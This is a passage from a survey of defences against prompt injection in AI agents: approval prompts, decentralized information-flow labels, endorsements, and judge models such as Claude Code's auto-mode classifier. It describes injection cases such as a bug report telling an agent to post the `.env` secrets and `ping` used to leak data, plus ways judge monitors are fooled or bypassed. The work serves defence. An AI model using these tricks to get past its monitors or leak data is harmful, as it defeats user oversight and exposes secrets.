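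Hossain and colleagues tested how much additional information helps. In one scenario, a user lets an agent send only summary totals to an auditor. An injected instruction makes the agent copy the raw invoices into `report.csv`. Later the agent asks to send the file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are allowed, and the filename looks harmless, so the user cannot spot the problem without knowing how the agent made the file.

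The researchers gave each of four prompts to 20 people, who together reviewed 120 unsafe and 120 legitimate requests per prompt:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The details, the user's original instruction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
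| The same facts, organized around the result of the action | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

The last design quotes the user's original restriction, shows the exact call, and briefly explains the call's result. In the example, the explanation is that the attachment contains data from raw invoice rows. The explanation links to the earlier steps so that the user can check it.

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. The difference between the last two designs may be due to chance, since the 95% interval for the adjusted difference runs from 19.7 points fewer unsafe approvals to 3.8 points more. For violations that depended on several linked steps, people approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with either design. Even with the best prompt, people approved almost a quarter of unsafe requests, and it took twice as long to read as the shortest one.

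This approach suits approvals better than endorsements. A system can work out what sending one file would reveal, but it cannot list everything an agent might do once the agent trusts an email. An endorsement prompt could instead show who wrote the email and which tools the agent could then use without asking again.

A prompt also has to get the user's attention. Li, Dai and colleagues found that few people noticed when a compromised agent misled them, and that warnings worked better if they interrupted the task. The interruptions helped most when people could easily check the problem, as in a cover letter, and much less with travel plans or emails. Some people who missed an attack trusted the agent more after seeing a warning, because they took it as a sign of a well-designed system. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests that prompts should show whether the user could undo an action, so that stronger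 warnings appear only for actions that are hard to reverse.

### Mistakes without an attacker

Label checks do not detect whether the agent has misunderstood its task. Kolluri and colleagues therefore say that information-flow control can replace human approval as a defence against attacks, but cannot replace it entirely. Anthropic has recorded one of its agents deleting branches of a shared code repository after misreading an instruction, and another trying to change the structure of a live database. The company attributes these mistakes to agents taking more initiative than the user intended. A label check allows such mistakes when the agent's context is trusted. An approval prompt that lists the branches to be deleted would at least give the user a chance to object.

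In Yan's study, the agent overstepped without any attacker, and human review stopped many of its unwanted actions, especially ones that affected privacy. People refused 79% of its attempts to announce publicly that the user was travelling and 65% of its attempts to read bank transactions. But they approved 88% of its unrequested calls to the airport, perhaps because a call to confirm a flight seemed helpful.

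*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that security rules should hold whether a harmful action comes from an attack, a model's error or a model's own aims. It also treats people as a weak point, since users can misread approval prompts and developers can forget to require them. For example, Claude Code once asked for approval of many shell commands but not of `ping`, which checks whether another computer responds. An attacker could use `ping` to send out secrets inside the address it looked up, without the user being asked.

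A refusal doesn't always stop the agent either. One person interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* refused several requests, but the agent kept trying other approaches, and the person could no longer tell whether it was staying within the limit. Refusing a call therefore works best when the system also blocks other ways of achieving the same result.

People can contribute information that no label or model has. Alex can phone the landlord and ask whether the account number has changed. With only the landlord's letter to go on, Alex would be no better at spotting a perfect forgery than the text-based authorizers that Fei and colleagues studied. A call takes much longer than the 16 to 39 seconds people typically spent on a prompt in Hossain and colleagues' study, so designers can expect such checks only for a few important actions. Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes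 to live systems themselves.

Current products make it difficult to involve people this selectively. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined 21 proposed permission systems and five commercial agents. Users of the commercial agents often had to choose between frequent prompts and automatic review by a model, and they had little control over that review. Michael and Roesner also consider Prudentia demanding, despite its savings, because it relies on users to make decisions during each task.

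## Rules fixed in advance by owners, developers and planners

Many of these decisions can be made before the agent starts work. An employer can state who may see its sales figures, a developer can state which tools refuse untrusted data, and a planner can write into its program which value from a file it will trust. If they do this before the agent reads anything a stranger wrote, the stranger cannot influence the decision, and nobody has to answer a prompt. But the employer, developer or planner has to foresee what the task will need.

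### Owners who can relax only their own rules

An agent often combines data from several parties, and each may want a say in who sees the result. Older information-flow systems left all declassification to a single authority that everyone had to trust. *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (Myers and Liskov, 1997) instead proposes a decentralized label model, in which each owner sets a policy on its own data and only that owner can relax it.

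A label in this model is a set of policies, each written "owner: readers". Let readers(*L*, *o*) be the people whom owner *o* allows to read data with label *L*. If *o* has no policy in the label, that means everyone. When a program combines data labelled *L*₁ and *L*₂, the result keeps the policies of all the owners, and for each owner

readers(*L*₁ ⊔ *L*₂, *o*) = readers(*L*₁, *o*) ∩ readers(*L*₂, *o*).

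Someone may read the result only if every owner allows it.

Suppose a caterer emails Alex a price offer. Alex asks the agent to draft a reply that also draws on Alex's travel dates and the employer's budget for the event. The owners start with these policies:

| Data | Owner | Readers the owner allows |
|---|---|---|
| Travel dates | Alex | Alex |
| Event budget | Employer | Alex, employer |
| Price offer | Caterer | Alex, employer, caterer |

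The draft carries all the policies, and only Alex is on every list. Before the agent can send the draft to the caterer, Alex has to add the caterer to the first list and the employer has to add the caterer to its own. Showing the draft to a rival caterer would also require the first caterer's consent.

A single combined list would show that only Alex may read the draft, but it wouldn't show whose permission is missing. Separate lists also limit the damage from an injection. An attacker who takes over an agent acting for Alex can relax Alex's policy but not the employer's.

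*Protecting Privacy Using the Decentralized Label Model* (Myers and Liskov, 2000) gives the example of Bob, who enters his tax data into a program he does not trust. The program also uses a secret database owned by the firm that wrote the program. The finished tax form contains information from both Bob's data and the database, so at first neither Bob nor the firm may read it. The firm can drop its own policy once it is satisfied that the form reveals little about the database. Bob's policy still applies, so the program can show him the form but cannot pass his data to anyone else, and he does not have to inspect the program's code.

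Owners can also let others act for them, but in the basic model they must hand over all of their powers or none. If the employer let Alex act for it, a hijacked agent could release everything the employer owns. It is safer to give the authority to a small program with one job. In Myers and Liskov's example of a bank, the only bank software that customers have to trust is a short piece of code that adds the amount of each request to the bank's secret total.

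### Checking everyone who influenced an action

A rule about readers cannot stop a stranger's email from triggering a payment. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *Conflux*, apply a similar principle to actions, which may proceed only if everyone who influenced them has permission to take them. Let *D* be the set of people whose information reached action *a*, and let *P*(*u*, *a*) mean that the organisation's existing access rules allow person *u* to take it. The system allows *a* only if

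*D* ≠ ∅ and *P*(*u*, *a*) for every *u* in *D*.

In one example, Ava asks an agent to update a customer's record with the status given in Ben's report. Ava and Ben both influence the update, so the system allows it only if both have permission to edit that record. Nobody has to endorse the report or write a new policy, because the organisation has already decided who may edit what.

The rule would block Alex's calendar request if the meeting request came from a stranger, because a stranger has no right to edit Alex's calendar. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt describe a remedy in which Alex records a grant that lets someone else take only one kind of action. They have specified such grants but not yet enabled them in the running system. Their proof that no forbidden action gets through assumes a complete record of who influenced the agent. They make no claim about how many useful tasks the system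 can finish, because cautious records of influence and additional policy checks can block legitimate work. Their AgentDojo runs only read data, so they do not test the defence on consequential actions. The rule is not meant to stop Ben from misusing permissions he really has.

### Rules about where data comes from

Developers can also write rules about which sources a system trusts, such as email from authenticated colleagues, documentation with a valid digital signature, or the parts of a web page that only the site can write. A signature shows that the holder of a particular key approved the text and that nobody has changed it since. Email authentication shows which internet domain sent a message.

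*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026) proposes a simple test for web pages. Part of a page is untrusted if anyone other than the site's operator can affect what it displays. A post's timestamp is therefore untrusted, because the person posting chooses the moment, but the word "created" in front of it is trusted. Numbers such as a count of open issues are also untrusted, even though they could hardly carry an instruction. Seip and colleagues prefer this test to judging what each element could carry because people and models can apply it consistently.

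Their system, SA-CUA, controls a whole computer through screenshots, mouse clicks and typing. It hides the entire screen from the planner, then reveals only the parts its rules mark as trusted. A model proposes the rules from the structure of a page, with all the text replaced by its length, so the text cannot persuade the model to trust it. A later check reads the text but can only remove rules.

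The researchers tested this on 160 screens they had labelled by hand. SA-CUA revealed no untrusted free text. Untrusted Content Masking, which starts with everything visible and hides what a model marks as untrusted, revealed 37% to 44% of it on the web pages. But SA-CUA also hid 56% to 77% of the trusted elements on those pages, while Untrusted Content Masking hid about 5%. Hiding trusted elements makes some tasks impossible, because an agent cannot click a button it cannot see.

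### Why proof of origin is not proof of safety

An attacker can do harm in several ways even when there is a perfect record of where data came from. For example, they can register the domain `acme-suppliers.com`, which adds one letter to a real supplier's `acme-supplies.com`, and send properly authenticated email from it. When Seip and colleagues ran ten of their hardest attacks against Anthropic's models, Claude Opus 5 resisted them all, while Claude Sonnet 5 failed twice, both times sending a confidential sales report to an impostor with a similar address.

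A genuine sender can also pass on something harmful, so the user naming a source does not make everything that source writes trustworthy. In one group of tests, the user tells the agent to ask a colleague, Mike Chen, how to change a setting, and the real Mike Chen's reply contains the attacker's instruction.

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) gives an example in which a stranger influences a tool call without supplying any of its text. The agent copies the tool name `repo.write_file` from the developer's list, but it chose that tool only because of the stranger's bug report.

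Santos-Grueiro proposes writing a policy in advance for every field of every tool. Trusted code can extract a value from untrusted data and approve it for one field only. For example, the agent may use a file path from an error log to choose which file to edit, but not as part of a command. The system rejects any field that the policy does not mention. In 400 test runs on code repositories, the agent safely completed 231 tasks, and no unauthorized value or action got through.

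### Endorsing a sender without endorsing the message

SA-CUA makes narrow exceptions of this kind without asking the user each time. If Alex asks the agent to find an email from a colleague, the system may have to endorse the sender's address, which it can check against Alex's contact book, but it does not have to endorse what the email says.

Each endorsement compares an untrusted value with an expectation that the system formed without seeing that value. Suppose the user wants a Python package that prints colored text, and the agent finds the name `termcolor` in a forum post. The planner can supply the expected name from its knowledge of Python, and ordinary code checks whether the two match. The forum post cannot influence the expectation, so an attacker can make the check fail but cannot make the agent accept an arbitrary name. If the check accepts several values, such as several version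 numbers, the attacker may still be able to choose among them.

The source of an expectation has to suit the value being checked. For example, a package's presence in Ubuntu's curated archive counts as evidence. Its presence in PyPI, the main public index of Python packages, does not, because an attacker can register a package there.

Commands take more work to check because one command can do several things. In one test, the agent reads a forum comment with instructions to stop the computer's printing service and then download a code repository. The planner has declared that the task involves downloading and writing files. The system splits the command into parts and approves the download after an independent lookup finds the same repository. It refuses to stop the printing service because that requires a power the planner never declared.

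If the user types "follow the instructions on screen", every value comes from the untrusted screen, so there is nothing to check the values against and no endorsement can be safe. SA-CUA therefore has a model examine each request at the start and return vague ones to the user. The user must describe the package well enough for the system to recognize the right one, but does not have to name it. More detail does not always help, because if the user wants a laptop that meets some condition, the only evidence may be the seller's own description. Seip and colleagues accept that SA-CUA cannot complete such a purchase without giving up its guarantee or asking the user.

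The table shows their results with GPT-5.6 Luna as the planner. In the first kind of attack, the attacker presents a harmful action as a necessary step. In the second, the attacker replaces a value the task needs, such as an email address. The last two columns come from tests without attacks.

| Agent | Harmful step: attacks succeeded | Harmful step: tasks completed | False value: attacks succeeded | False value: tasks completed | Desktop tasks completed | Website tasks completed |
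|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 38.5% | 98.5% | 38.5% | 60.3% | 58.3% | 91.9% |
| CaMeL, adapted to computer use | 0% | 27.7% | 0% | 29.5% | 8.3% | 19.2% |
| SA-CUA | 0% | 81.5% | 0% | 69.2% | 38.9% | 49.5% |

Checking values against independent sources helps, since SA-CUA completed far more tasks than CaMeL without letting any attack through. It still failed a third of the desktop tasks and almost half of the website tasks that the undefended agent could do, partly because many of them require acting on text that nobody can verify.

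The attack results also depend on some favourable choices. When SA-CUA judged a request too vague, the researchers automatically substituted a more specific version, whereas a real user would have to write one. They treated GitHub as a reliable reference, although anyone can publish there, because some tasks would otherwise have been impossible. SA-CUA does not protect secrets, so an agent could still post confidential information in public.

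### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Developers can already use some of these ideas in a released product. In May 2026 Microsoft added FIDES, the system designed by Costa and colleagues, to Agent Framework, its software for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes the feature as experimental, and developers have to switch it on.

The developer writes both the labels and the policies, and the framework tracks the labels and checks the policies. For example, a tool that reads bug reports from GitHub marks their text as untrusted. A policy can block a tool that changes files from running in an untrusted context, or block a tool that posts public comments once the agent has read private data.

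In Microsoft's example, a bug report contains a hidden instruction to read the file `.env`, which holds passwords, and post its contents as a comment. If the planner follows the instruction, the framework lets it read the file but marks the contents as private, then blocks the comment because it would be public. The framework would also block a call to overwrite a file, because the context is untrusted.

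A developer can turn each blocked call into a request for the user's approval. The prompt shows the tool and the label that caused the block, but Microsoft acknowledges that the prompt does not fully explain why the user has to decide. The user faces the same difficulties as with any other approval prompt.

The defaults matter because many developers will keep them. By default, the framework hides untrusted results from the planner and sends them to a quarantined model when the agent needs a summary. But if the developer forgets to label a tool, the framework treats everything the tool returns as trusted and public. A missing label on an email tool would let strangers' messages pass every integrity check. SA-CUA and Santos-Grueiro's system have the opposite default, so a missing rule makes them less useful rather than less secure. Microsoft has asked developers whether it should adopt that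 default.

### Endorsements that the planner writes

A developer who labels email as untrusted cannot know that Alex will one day ask the agent to pay a bill from a particular file. The planner can know this, because it reads Alex's request. In Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues built, the planner may include endorsements in the program it writes before it sees any outside data. In simplified form, a plan to pay a bill could look like this:

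```
bill = read_file("bill.txt")
account = endorse(quarantined_model("Find the account number", bill))
amount = quarantined_model("Find the amount", bill)
send_money(account, amount)
```

The bill can influence which account number the program endorses, but not whether it endorses one. The payment tool requires a trusted recipient but not a trusted amount. Without the endorsement, the program would stop at the last line.

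Garby and colleagues measured what these endorsements add on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, which they ran three times each. The table shows the runs without attacks, with 95% confidence intervals:

| Agent | Model | Runs completed | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori, endorsements on | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 75.0% ± 20.0 |
| Randori, endorsements off | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 | 62.5% ± 24.2 |
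| Randori, endorsements on | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 64.6% ± 22.0 |
| Randori, endorsements off | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 | 54.2% ± 23.3 |
| Randori, endorsements on | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 75.0% ± 18.9 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 66.7% ± 23.4 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 70.8% ± 21.4 |
| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 37.5% ± 26.6 |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 37.5% ± 26.6 |

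Endorsements added six completed runs with one model and five with the other. The intervals overlap too much for these results alone to prove a benefit, but there is good reason to expect one, because three of the 16 tasks require the agent to read a file and act on its contents, which Randori cannot do without an endorsement. Those tasks account for nine of the 48 runs, so a gain of five or six is about as large as one could expect.

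With endorsements on, two attacks succeeded in 1,296 runs, both against GPT-5.2 on the task in which the attacker replaces the payment details in a file. That rate somewhat overstates the protection endorsement gives, because in about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the plan contains no step the attacker could use, so the attack would fail anyway. In the remaining combinations, attacks succeeded in two of 423 runs.

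With CaMeL, developers have to choose between safety and usefulness. With its policies on, no attack succeeded in the 588 attacked runs that finished, but it completed only half as many unattacked runs as Randori did with GPT-5.2. With its policies off, it completed about as many as Randori, and five attacks succeeded in 622 runs. The intervals for Randori and CaMeL overlap slightly even when CaMeL's policies are on. Randori also has looser policies, which make its tasks easier to complete. For example, its tool for scheduling a future payment checks that the amount is trusted but not the recipient, so an attacker's account number could pass without endorsement. Garby and colleagues deliberately simplified the policies for a first version.

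The theorem behind Randori guarantees that secrets stay safe whatever the planner endorses, but nothing stops the planner from endorsing too much. Garby and colleagues suggest checking plans automatically before they run, but have not yet tried this.

Writing the plan first does not guarantee a narrow plan. One banking task tells the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two runs with CaMeL's policies off, the planner wrote a program with a separate branch for each tool, so that it could carry out whatever the file asked. An attacker could make the program do almost anything by changing the file, without changing the program itself.

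### Turning a request into a policy

Rules written early work best when somebody knows the task in advance. The developer of a phone weather app can list the permissions it needs because the app will always do roughly the same thing. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that an agent has no such fixed purpose. Its user describes a new task in ordinary language and may change it halfway through, so the right permissions change too. A fixed plan can fail when the agent discovers new steps along the way, as CaMeL's did on every AgentDyn task.

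Web browsers face a similar problem when a page loads new code, and they restrict what that code may do. The paper notes that browsers usually know the address each piece of code came from, and that the site's owner has decided which code to include. But an agent often has to work with instructions whose source is unclear and which nobody chose beforehand.

A system could write a new policy for each request, but the paper describes reliably translating ordinary language into formal rules as an unsolved problem. Suppose Alex types, "Pay the landlord what the letter says." This could mean that the agent should take the amount from the letter and use the account Alex has saved, or that it should take both the amount and the account from the letter, perhaps because the landlord has changed banks. A policy based on the first reading would block a genuine change of account, while one based on the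 second would let a forged letter redirect the payment.

The paper recommends using formal verification to prove that a generated policy enforces the intended restrictions. That proof needs a precise statement of what Alex intended, which Alex's request doesn't include. It would help to ask Alex to be more specific, as SA-CUA does when a request is vague, but Alex may not know before the agent opens the letter that the account number will matter. People who write policies by hand also make mistakes, and an administrator may grant too much access to keep an agent working.

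## Letting another model decide at run time

If nobody can say which account to trust until the agent opens the landlord's letter, a second model could judge at that point whether to allow the exception. It can compare Alex's request with the letter and the proposed payment. Designs differ in what they let this model decide, from whether text can reach the planner to whether a single tool call can go ahead.

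### Admitting text that the task needs

*ATrust* (Zhang and Lu, 2026) presents a small model that filters each tool result before it reaches the planner. The model keeps what the task needs and removes everything else, harmful or not.

In one of their examples, a user with $1,810 in the bank asks the agent to send Alice everything except the cost of the electricity bill. The electricity company's web page contains a form for fetching the bill, along with an injected instruction to enter the user's bank details on another site. ATrust handles the page as follows:

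1. The judge receives the user's request, everything it has admitted so far, the latest tool call and the page.
2. It splits the page into pieces, each holding one complete item of information, and tags each piece as related or unrelated to the task.
3. It rewrites the related pieces without greetings and other filler, then adds them to the admitted text.
4. The planner chooses its next call using the admitted text.

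The judge removed the injection and kept the form, so the agent found the bill of $156.90 and sent Alice $1,653.10. When the filter PIGuard discarded the whole page instead, the agent guessed that the bill was $100 and sent too much.

Admitting a piece of text is an endorsement, because the planner may then act on it. Each endorsement also affects later ones. If *E*_t is the admitted text after step *t*, *o*_t the new tool result and *D* the judge, then

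*E*_t = Append(*E*_{t−1}, *D*(*o*_t, *E*_{t−1})),

where *E*₀ is the user's request. These are the results on AgentDyn, the benchmark on which CaMeL completed almost nothing. Each cell gives the figure without a defence, then with ATrust:

| Agent's model | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 45.0% → 43.3% | 37.0% → 46.2% | 50.2% → 3.6% |
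| GPT-4o | 53.3% → 63.3% | 55.5% → 61.1% | 37.8% → 4.4% |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 35.0% → 40.0% | 35.5% → 40.1% | 4.6% → 0.4% |
| Qwen3-Coder | 18.3% → 53.3% | 15.8% → 53.9% | 14.6% → 4.5% |
| Kimi-K2.5 | 71.7% → 73.3% | 54.2% → 70.5% | 11.7% → 1.3% |

With ATrust, at most 1.9% of attacks on AgentDojo succeeded for any of the five models. ATrust used only 9% to 16% more tokens than an undefended agent.

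Most of the security came from training the judge for this job. Zhang and Lu trained a model with 4 billion parameters on 1,030 examples that mixed useful tool results with injections and harmless clutter. When they replaced it with GPT-4o-mini, 23.7% of attacks succeeded, and with the far larger Qwen3-Coder, 35.1% did. Security also depended on what the judge compared each result with. When it used only the user's original request, 14.0% of attacks got through.

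Zhang and Lu also tried two attacks aimed at the judge. One used an automated search for better wording, which raised the success rate from 3.6% to 8.3%. The other added a false claim that the source was trustworthy, which raised it to 12.1%.

ATrust relies on injected instructions being unrelated to the user's task, but false data may be relevant to that task. If an attacker changed the amount on the electricity bill, the judge would have no reason to drop the false amount, because the task needs an amount.

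### Checking messages to unknown recipients

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, a system that uses a judge to protect private records from outsiders who talk to the agent. In one scenario, Jane's agent has access to Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his ex-wife Emily wants to learn it. Emily may also ask for something harmless, such as general advice on supporting a co-parent. Once the agent has read the diagnosis, ordinary labels would block it from sharing either the diagnosis or the advice.

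FlowSeal decides each case in these steps:

1. Ordinary code intercepts every call that writes or shares something.
2. If the data's owner has approved the recipient, the code allows the call. If the recipient is on a blocked list, it refuses.
3. For any other recipient, the code sends a separate model the protected records that may have influenced the message, together with the message itself. The model does not see the agent's conversation with Emily.
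4. The model answers SAFE if the message contains nothing derived from the records, and BLOCKED otherwise.
5. After a BLOCKED answer, the agent can ask the owner for permission or write a different message.

The judge therefore decides only whether the restrictive label on the message was necessary, while Mark still decides whether Emily deserves to know the diagnosis.

Shim and colleagues tested eight attacks that use ordinary conversation, such as asking the agent to add its notes to a shared page. They did not test prompt injection. Against an agent with a detailed privacy prompt, the shared-page attack extracted 52.2% of the private items. An attack that asks the agent to tidy a list of true and false records extracted 75.6%. With FlowSeal, these two attacks extracted 0.5% and 2.3%, and none of the eight extracted more than 3.3%. In a smaller test on real Gmail and Notion accounts, the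 tidying attack extracted nothing.

The researchers then replaced the judge with a fixed answer:

| Judge's answer | Private items leaked in the shared-page attack | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Decided case by case | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

The judge accounts for nearly all of the system's usefulness in this test. The 0% result is an extreme case, because every recipient was unknown and the owners ignored all requests for permission. In a separate test where owners consented, FlowSeal shared only 32.7% of the items it should have, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for four other defences. This was largely because FlowSeal's agent asked for consent less often.

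Shim and colleagues prove that no message derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorized recipient unless the judge wrongly answers SAFE, but the theorem does not establish how often that happens. They found that the judge's misses were mainly paraphrases, and they suspect that an attacker could split one fact across several messages that each look harmless.

### Automatic approval in Claude Code

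The most widely used of these judges approves actions. In Claude Code's auto mode, a model called the classifier replaces most of the permission prompts that users tire of reading. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, each action goes through these steps:

1. Rules that allow an action, forbid it or require a prompt apply first, with a few exceptions.
2. Most read-only actions and edits inside the project folder go ahead without review.
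3. The classifier judges almost everything else, including most shell commands and web requests.
4. If it blocks an action, the agent receives a reason and can try something safer. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the user gets prompts again.

When Claude Code sends the request itself, the classifier receives the user's messages, the project's instruction file and the agent's tool calls, except for simple lookups. It does not receive tool results, where injections usually arrive, or the agent's explanations, which might lead it to allow something harmful. In Anthropic's example, a file contains an instruction for the agent to post its stored passwords to a website. The classifier can reject the post without access to the file, because the user never asked for the post. But if the agent cancels "job abc123", the classifier can't determine whether that name came from a search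 or the agent made it up.

A separate check scans tool results for injections and adds a warning for the agent. The classifier works in two stages. The first is fast, answers yes or no, and leans towards blocking. The second is slower and reasons about whatever the first flagged. In Anthropic's tests with Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the classifier, the fast stage alone blocked 8.5% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by employees, while both stages together blocked 0.4%. The default classifier is now Claude Sonnet 5.

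Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, tested auto mode independently on ambiguous requests, such as cancelling "my stale job" when several jobs have similar names. The table compares their result with those that Anthropic published:

| Dangerous actions in the test | Share the classifier allowed |
|---|---|
| 52 real cases in which the agent exceeded its instructions | 17% |
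| 1,000 generated attempts to send data out | 5.7% |
| 1,053 dangerous commands also shown to human testers | 11% |
| Synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, a safety organisation, after Anthropic had improved the classifier | 7% |
| Ambiguous requests (Ji and colleagues) | 70.3% |

Ji and colleagues warn against comparing their figure directly with Anthropic's 17%, because they deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets close together. Their test involved no attacker. The classifier also blocked 31.9% of the safe actions it judged. File edits skip the classifier, and when they are included, 81.0% of unsafe actions went through. When a command was missing, the agent often instead edited the file that listed the jobs or stored items.

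Anthropic found that when the classifier missed one of the 52 real cases, it had usually detected the danger but was wrong about what the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) has not asked the agent to overwrite the project's history.

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside tester, to run 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the attacks succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. But without auto mode, only 0.09% succeeded against Anthropic's latest models, so auto mode had almost nothing to stop. Results for OpenAI's Codex better show how much a judge can help. With GPT-5.6 Sol, 19.03% of attacks succeeded when the agent had full access and 5.83% when a model reviewed its actions. OpenAI has since updated that reviewer. Willison hoped Anthropic had solved the problem but wanted more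 independent confirmation.

### What a judge can see that a rule cannot

Sending code to the company's private repository is routine, but sending it to a public one could be a serious leak. A developer can write a rule for that, but not for every restriction a user might mention. If Alex tells Claude Code not to publish anything before Alex has reviewed it, its classifier blocks later attempts to publish, even if the standard rules would allow them. FlowSeal's judge can distinguish general advice from a disguised diagnosis, which a label cannot do. ATrust can admit an instruction that nobody expected when the task began.

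In Anthropic's study with paid testers, a judge model caught 89% of the dangerous commands, most of which people missed, and did as well late in a session as at the start. It blocked 800 commands that a person had approved, while people blocked only 6 that it had allowed.

Evidence from real use supports the same conclusion, but less strongly. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained seriously harmful actions that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users choose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

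### Why an error rate is not a guarantee

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects to using a model as a reference monitor, the component that permits or rejects each action according to a policy. Engineers can check an ordinary monitor against a precise specification, and although cryptographic systems can fail by chance, mathematicians can bound the probability of failure under stated assumptions. But nobody has specified which actions a model should allow after every possible history, so nobody can prove that it will decide correctly. Making the model give the same answer to the same input doesn't solve this, because an attacker can change the input.

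Text can mislead a judge model just as it can mislead a planner. Crosley reports in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that a researcher got past auto mode in most of a small number of runs in August 2026.

Anthropic argues that its two layers reinforce each other, because an attack must get past the check on tool results and then produce an action that the classifier, which never saw the injected text, classifies as safe. The position paper replies that attackers can develop a separate trick for each model and combine them. Multiplying the two failure rates would therefore underestimate the combined failure rate, unless the failures were independent.

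Improving a judge can also undo earlier protection. When Anthropic strengthened its classifier after Apollo's first attacks, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. This was a large net gain, but users couldn't rely on a particular attack staying blocked. With an explicit policy, removing an action from the list of permitted ones leaves every earlier exclusion in place, which the position paper counts as an advantage.

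Fixed rules, though, can miss what the user meant, as with the request to pay the landlord. If nobody has written a rule for a request such as "clean up my branches", a judge model that is usually right may prevent more harm than fixed rules would. But even a small error rate may be too high for a payment to a stranger, since attackers can keep trying.

### What hard limits leave to the judge

The paper does not reject judges altogether. It supports letting models interpret requests while independent code authorizes protected actions. Claude Code partly works this way, as Anthropic describes in its instructions for configuring auto mode:

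| Type of rule | What applies it | Can the user's request override it? |
|---|---|---|
| `permissions.deny` | Ordinary code, before the classifier | No |
| `permissions.ask` | Ordinary code, which prompts the user | No, the user must answer the prompt |
| `hard_deny` | The classifier, reading a rule in plain English | No |
| `soft_deny` | The classifier, reading a rule in plain English | Yes, if it describes the exact action |

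Even a `hard_deny` rule works only if the classifier recognizes that it applies. Rules that code enforces don't depend on the classifier, but they have to match the command as written. For example, a rule requiring a prompt for `git push` misses some other ways of writing the same command.

Within these limits, the classifier still decides whether a destination is outside the organisation, whether data is sensitive, and whether the user's words cover the action. Most of the misses Anthropic examined were in the last of these decisions, so hard limits reduce the damage from a wrong decision but don't make one less likely.

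Other designs give the judging model less power. In *Agent libOS* (2026), a system for running agents with limited permissions, the model can block an action or send it for further review but can never allow one. If the model fails, the system is no less secure than it would be without it. But the model also can't grant the exception that Alex's calendar request needs, so a person or a rule still has to do that.

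A model may also suggest values for single fields, but Santos-Grueiro's trusted code decides whether to accept them. The code converts each suggestion to a standard form and checks it against reliable data. This works for paths and dates because code can check them. No such check exists for whether a paragraph of advice reveals a diagnosis, so FlowSeal has to accept a model's answer.

### Which label the verdict should carry

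A judge that reads a stranger's email produces output derived from untrusted data. Under the usual rule for language models, its verdict should therefore be untrusted as well. Consider an agent that endorses an email if a judge finds it related to the task:

```
verdict = judge(request, email)
if verdict == "related":
    text = endorse(email)
```

The stranger can influence `verdict`, so in LLMBDA this endorsement "launders nothing" (*The LLMbda Calculus*, 2026). For the code to work, the developer must endorse the verdict first. The judge then decides each case, but the developer has decided in advance that its verdict is sufficient.

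That decision matters more for some verdicts than for others. In the calendar task, a yes-or-no answer determines whether one known action happens. The verdict here is also just one bit, but a yes lets the planner act on an email of any length.

Hiding tool results from the judge gives an attacker fewer ways to influence it, though it does not make the verdict trusted. Claude Code's classifier does not see tool results, but it reads tool calls written by an agent that has seen them, so an attacker can still influence it indirectly.

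The verdict in FlowSeal should be secret as well as untrusted, because it depends on Mark's records. The judge gives no explanation, to avoid revealing anything about those records, but Emily may still learn something from whether a message arrives. Like the answer based on Priya's preview, this verdict would fail the test of transparent endorsement, because Emily has no right to read the records it depends on.

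A system can also act on a verdict without changing any labels, just as a user can approve an action without endorsing the data. *APPA* (2026), another information-flow system for agents, lets a rule, a person or a model allow one exact call that would otherwise fail the label check. The permission works only once, and the system logs its use. A wrong verdict then affects only that call, whereas in ATrust a wrongly admitted sentence stays in the planner's context and influences what the judge admits next.
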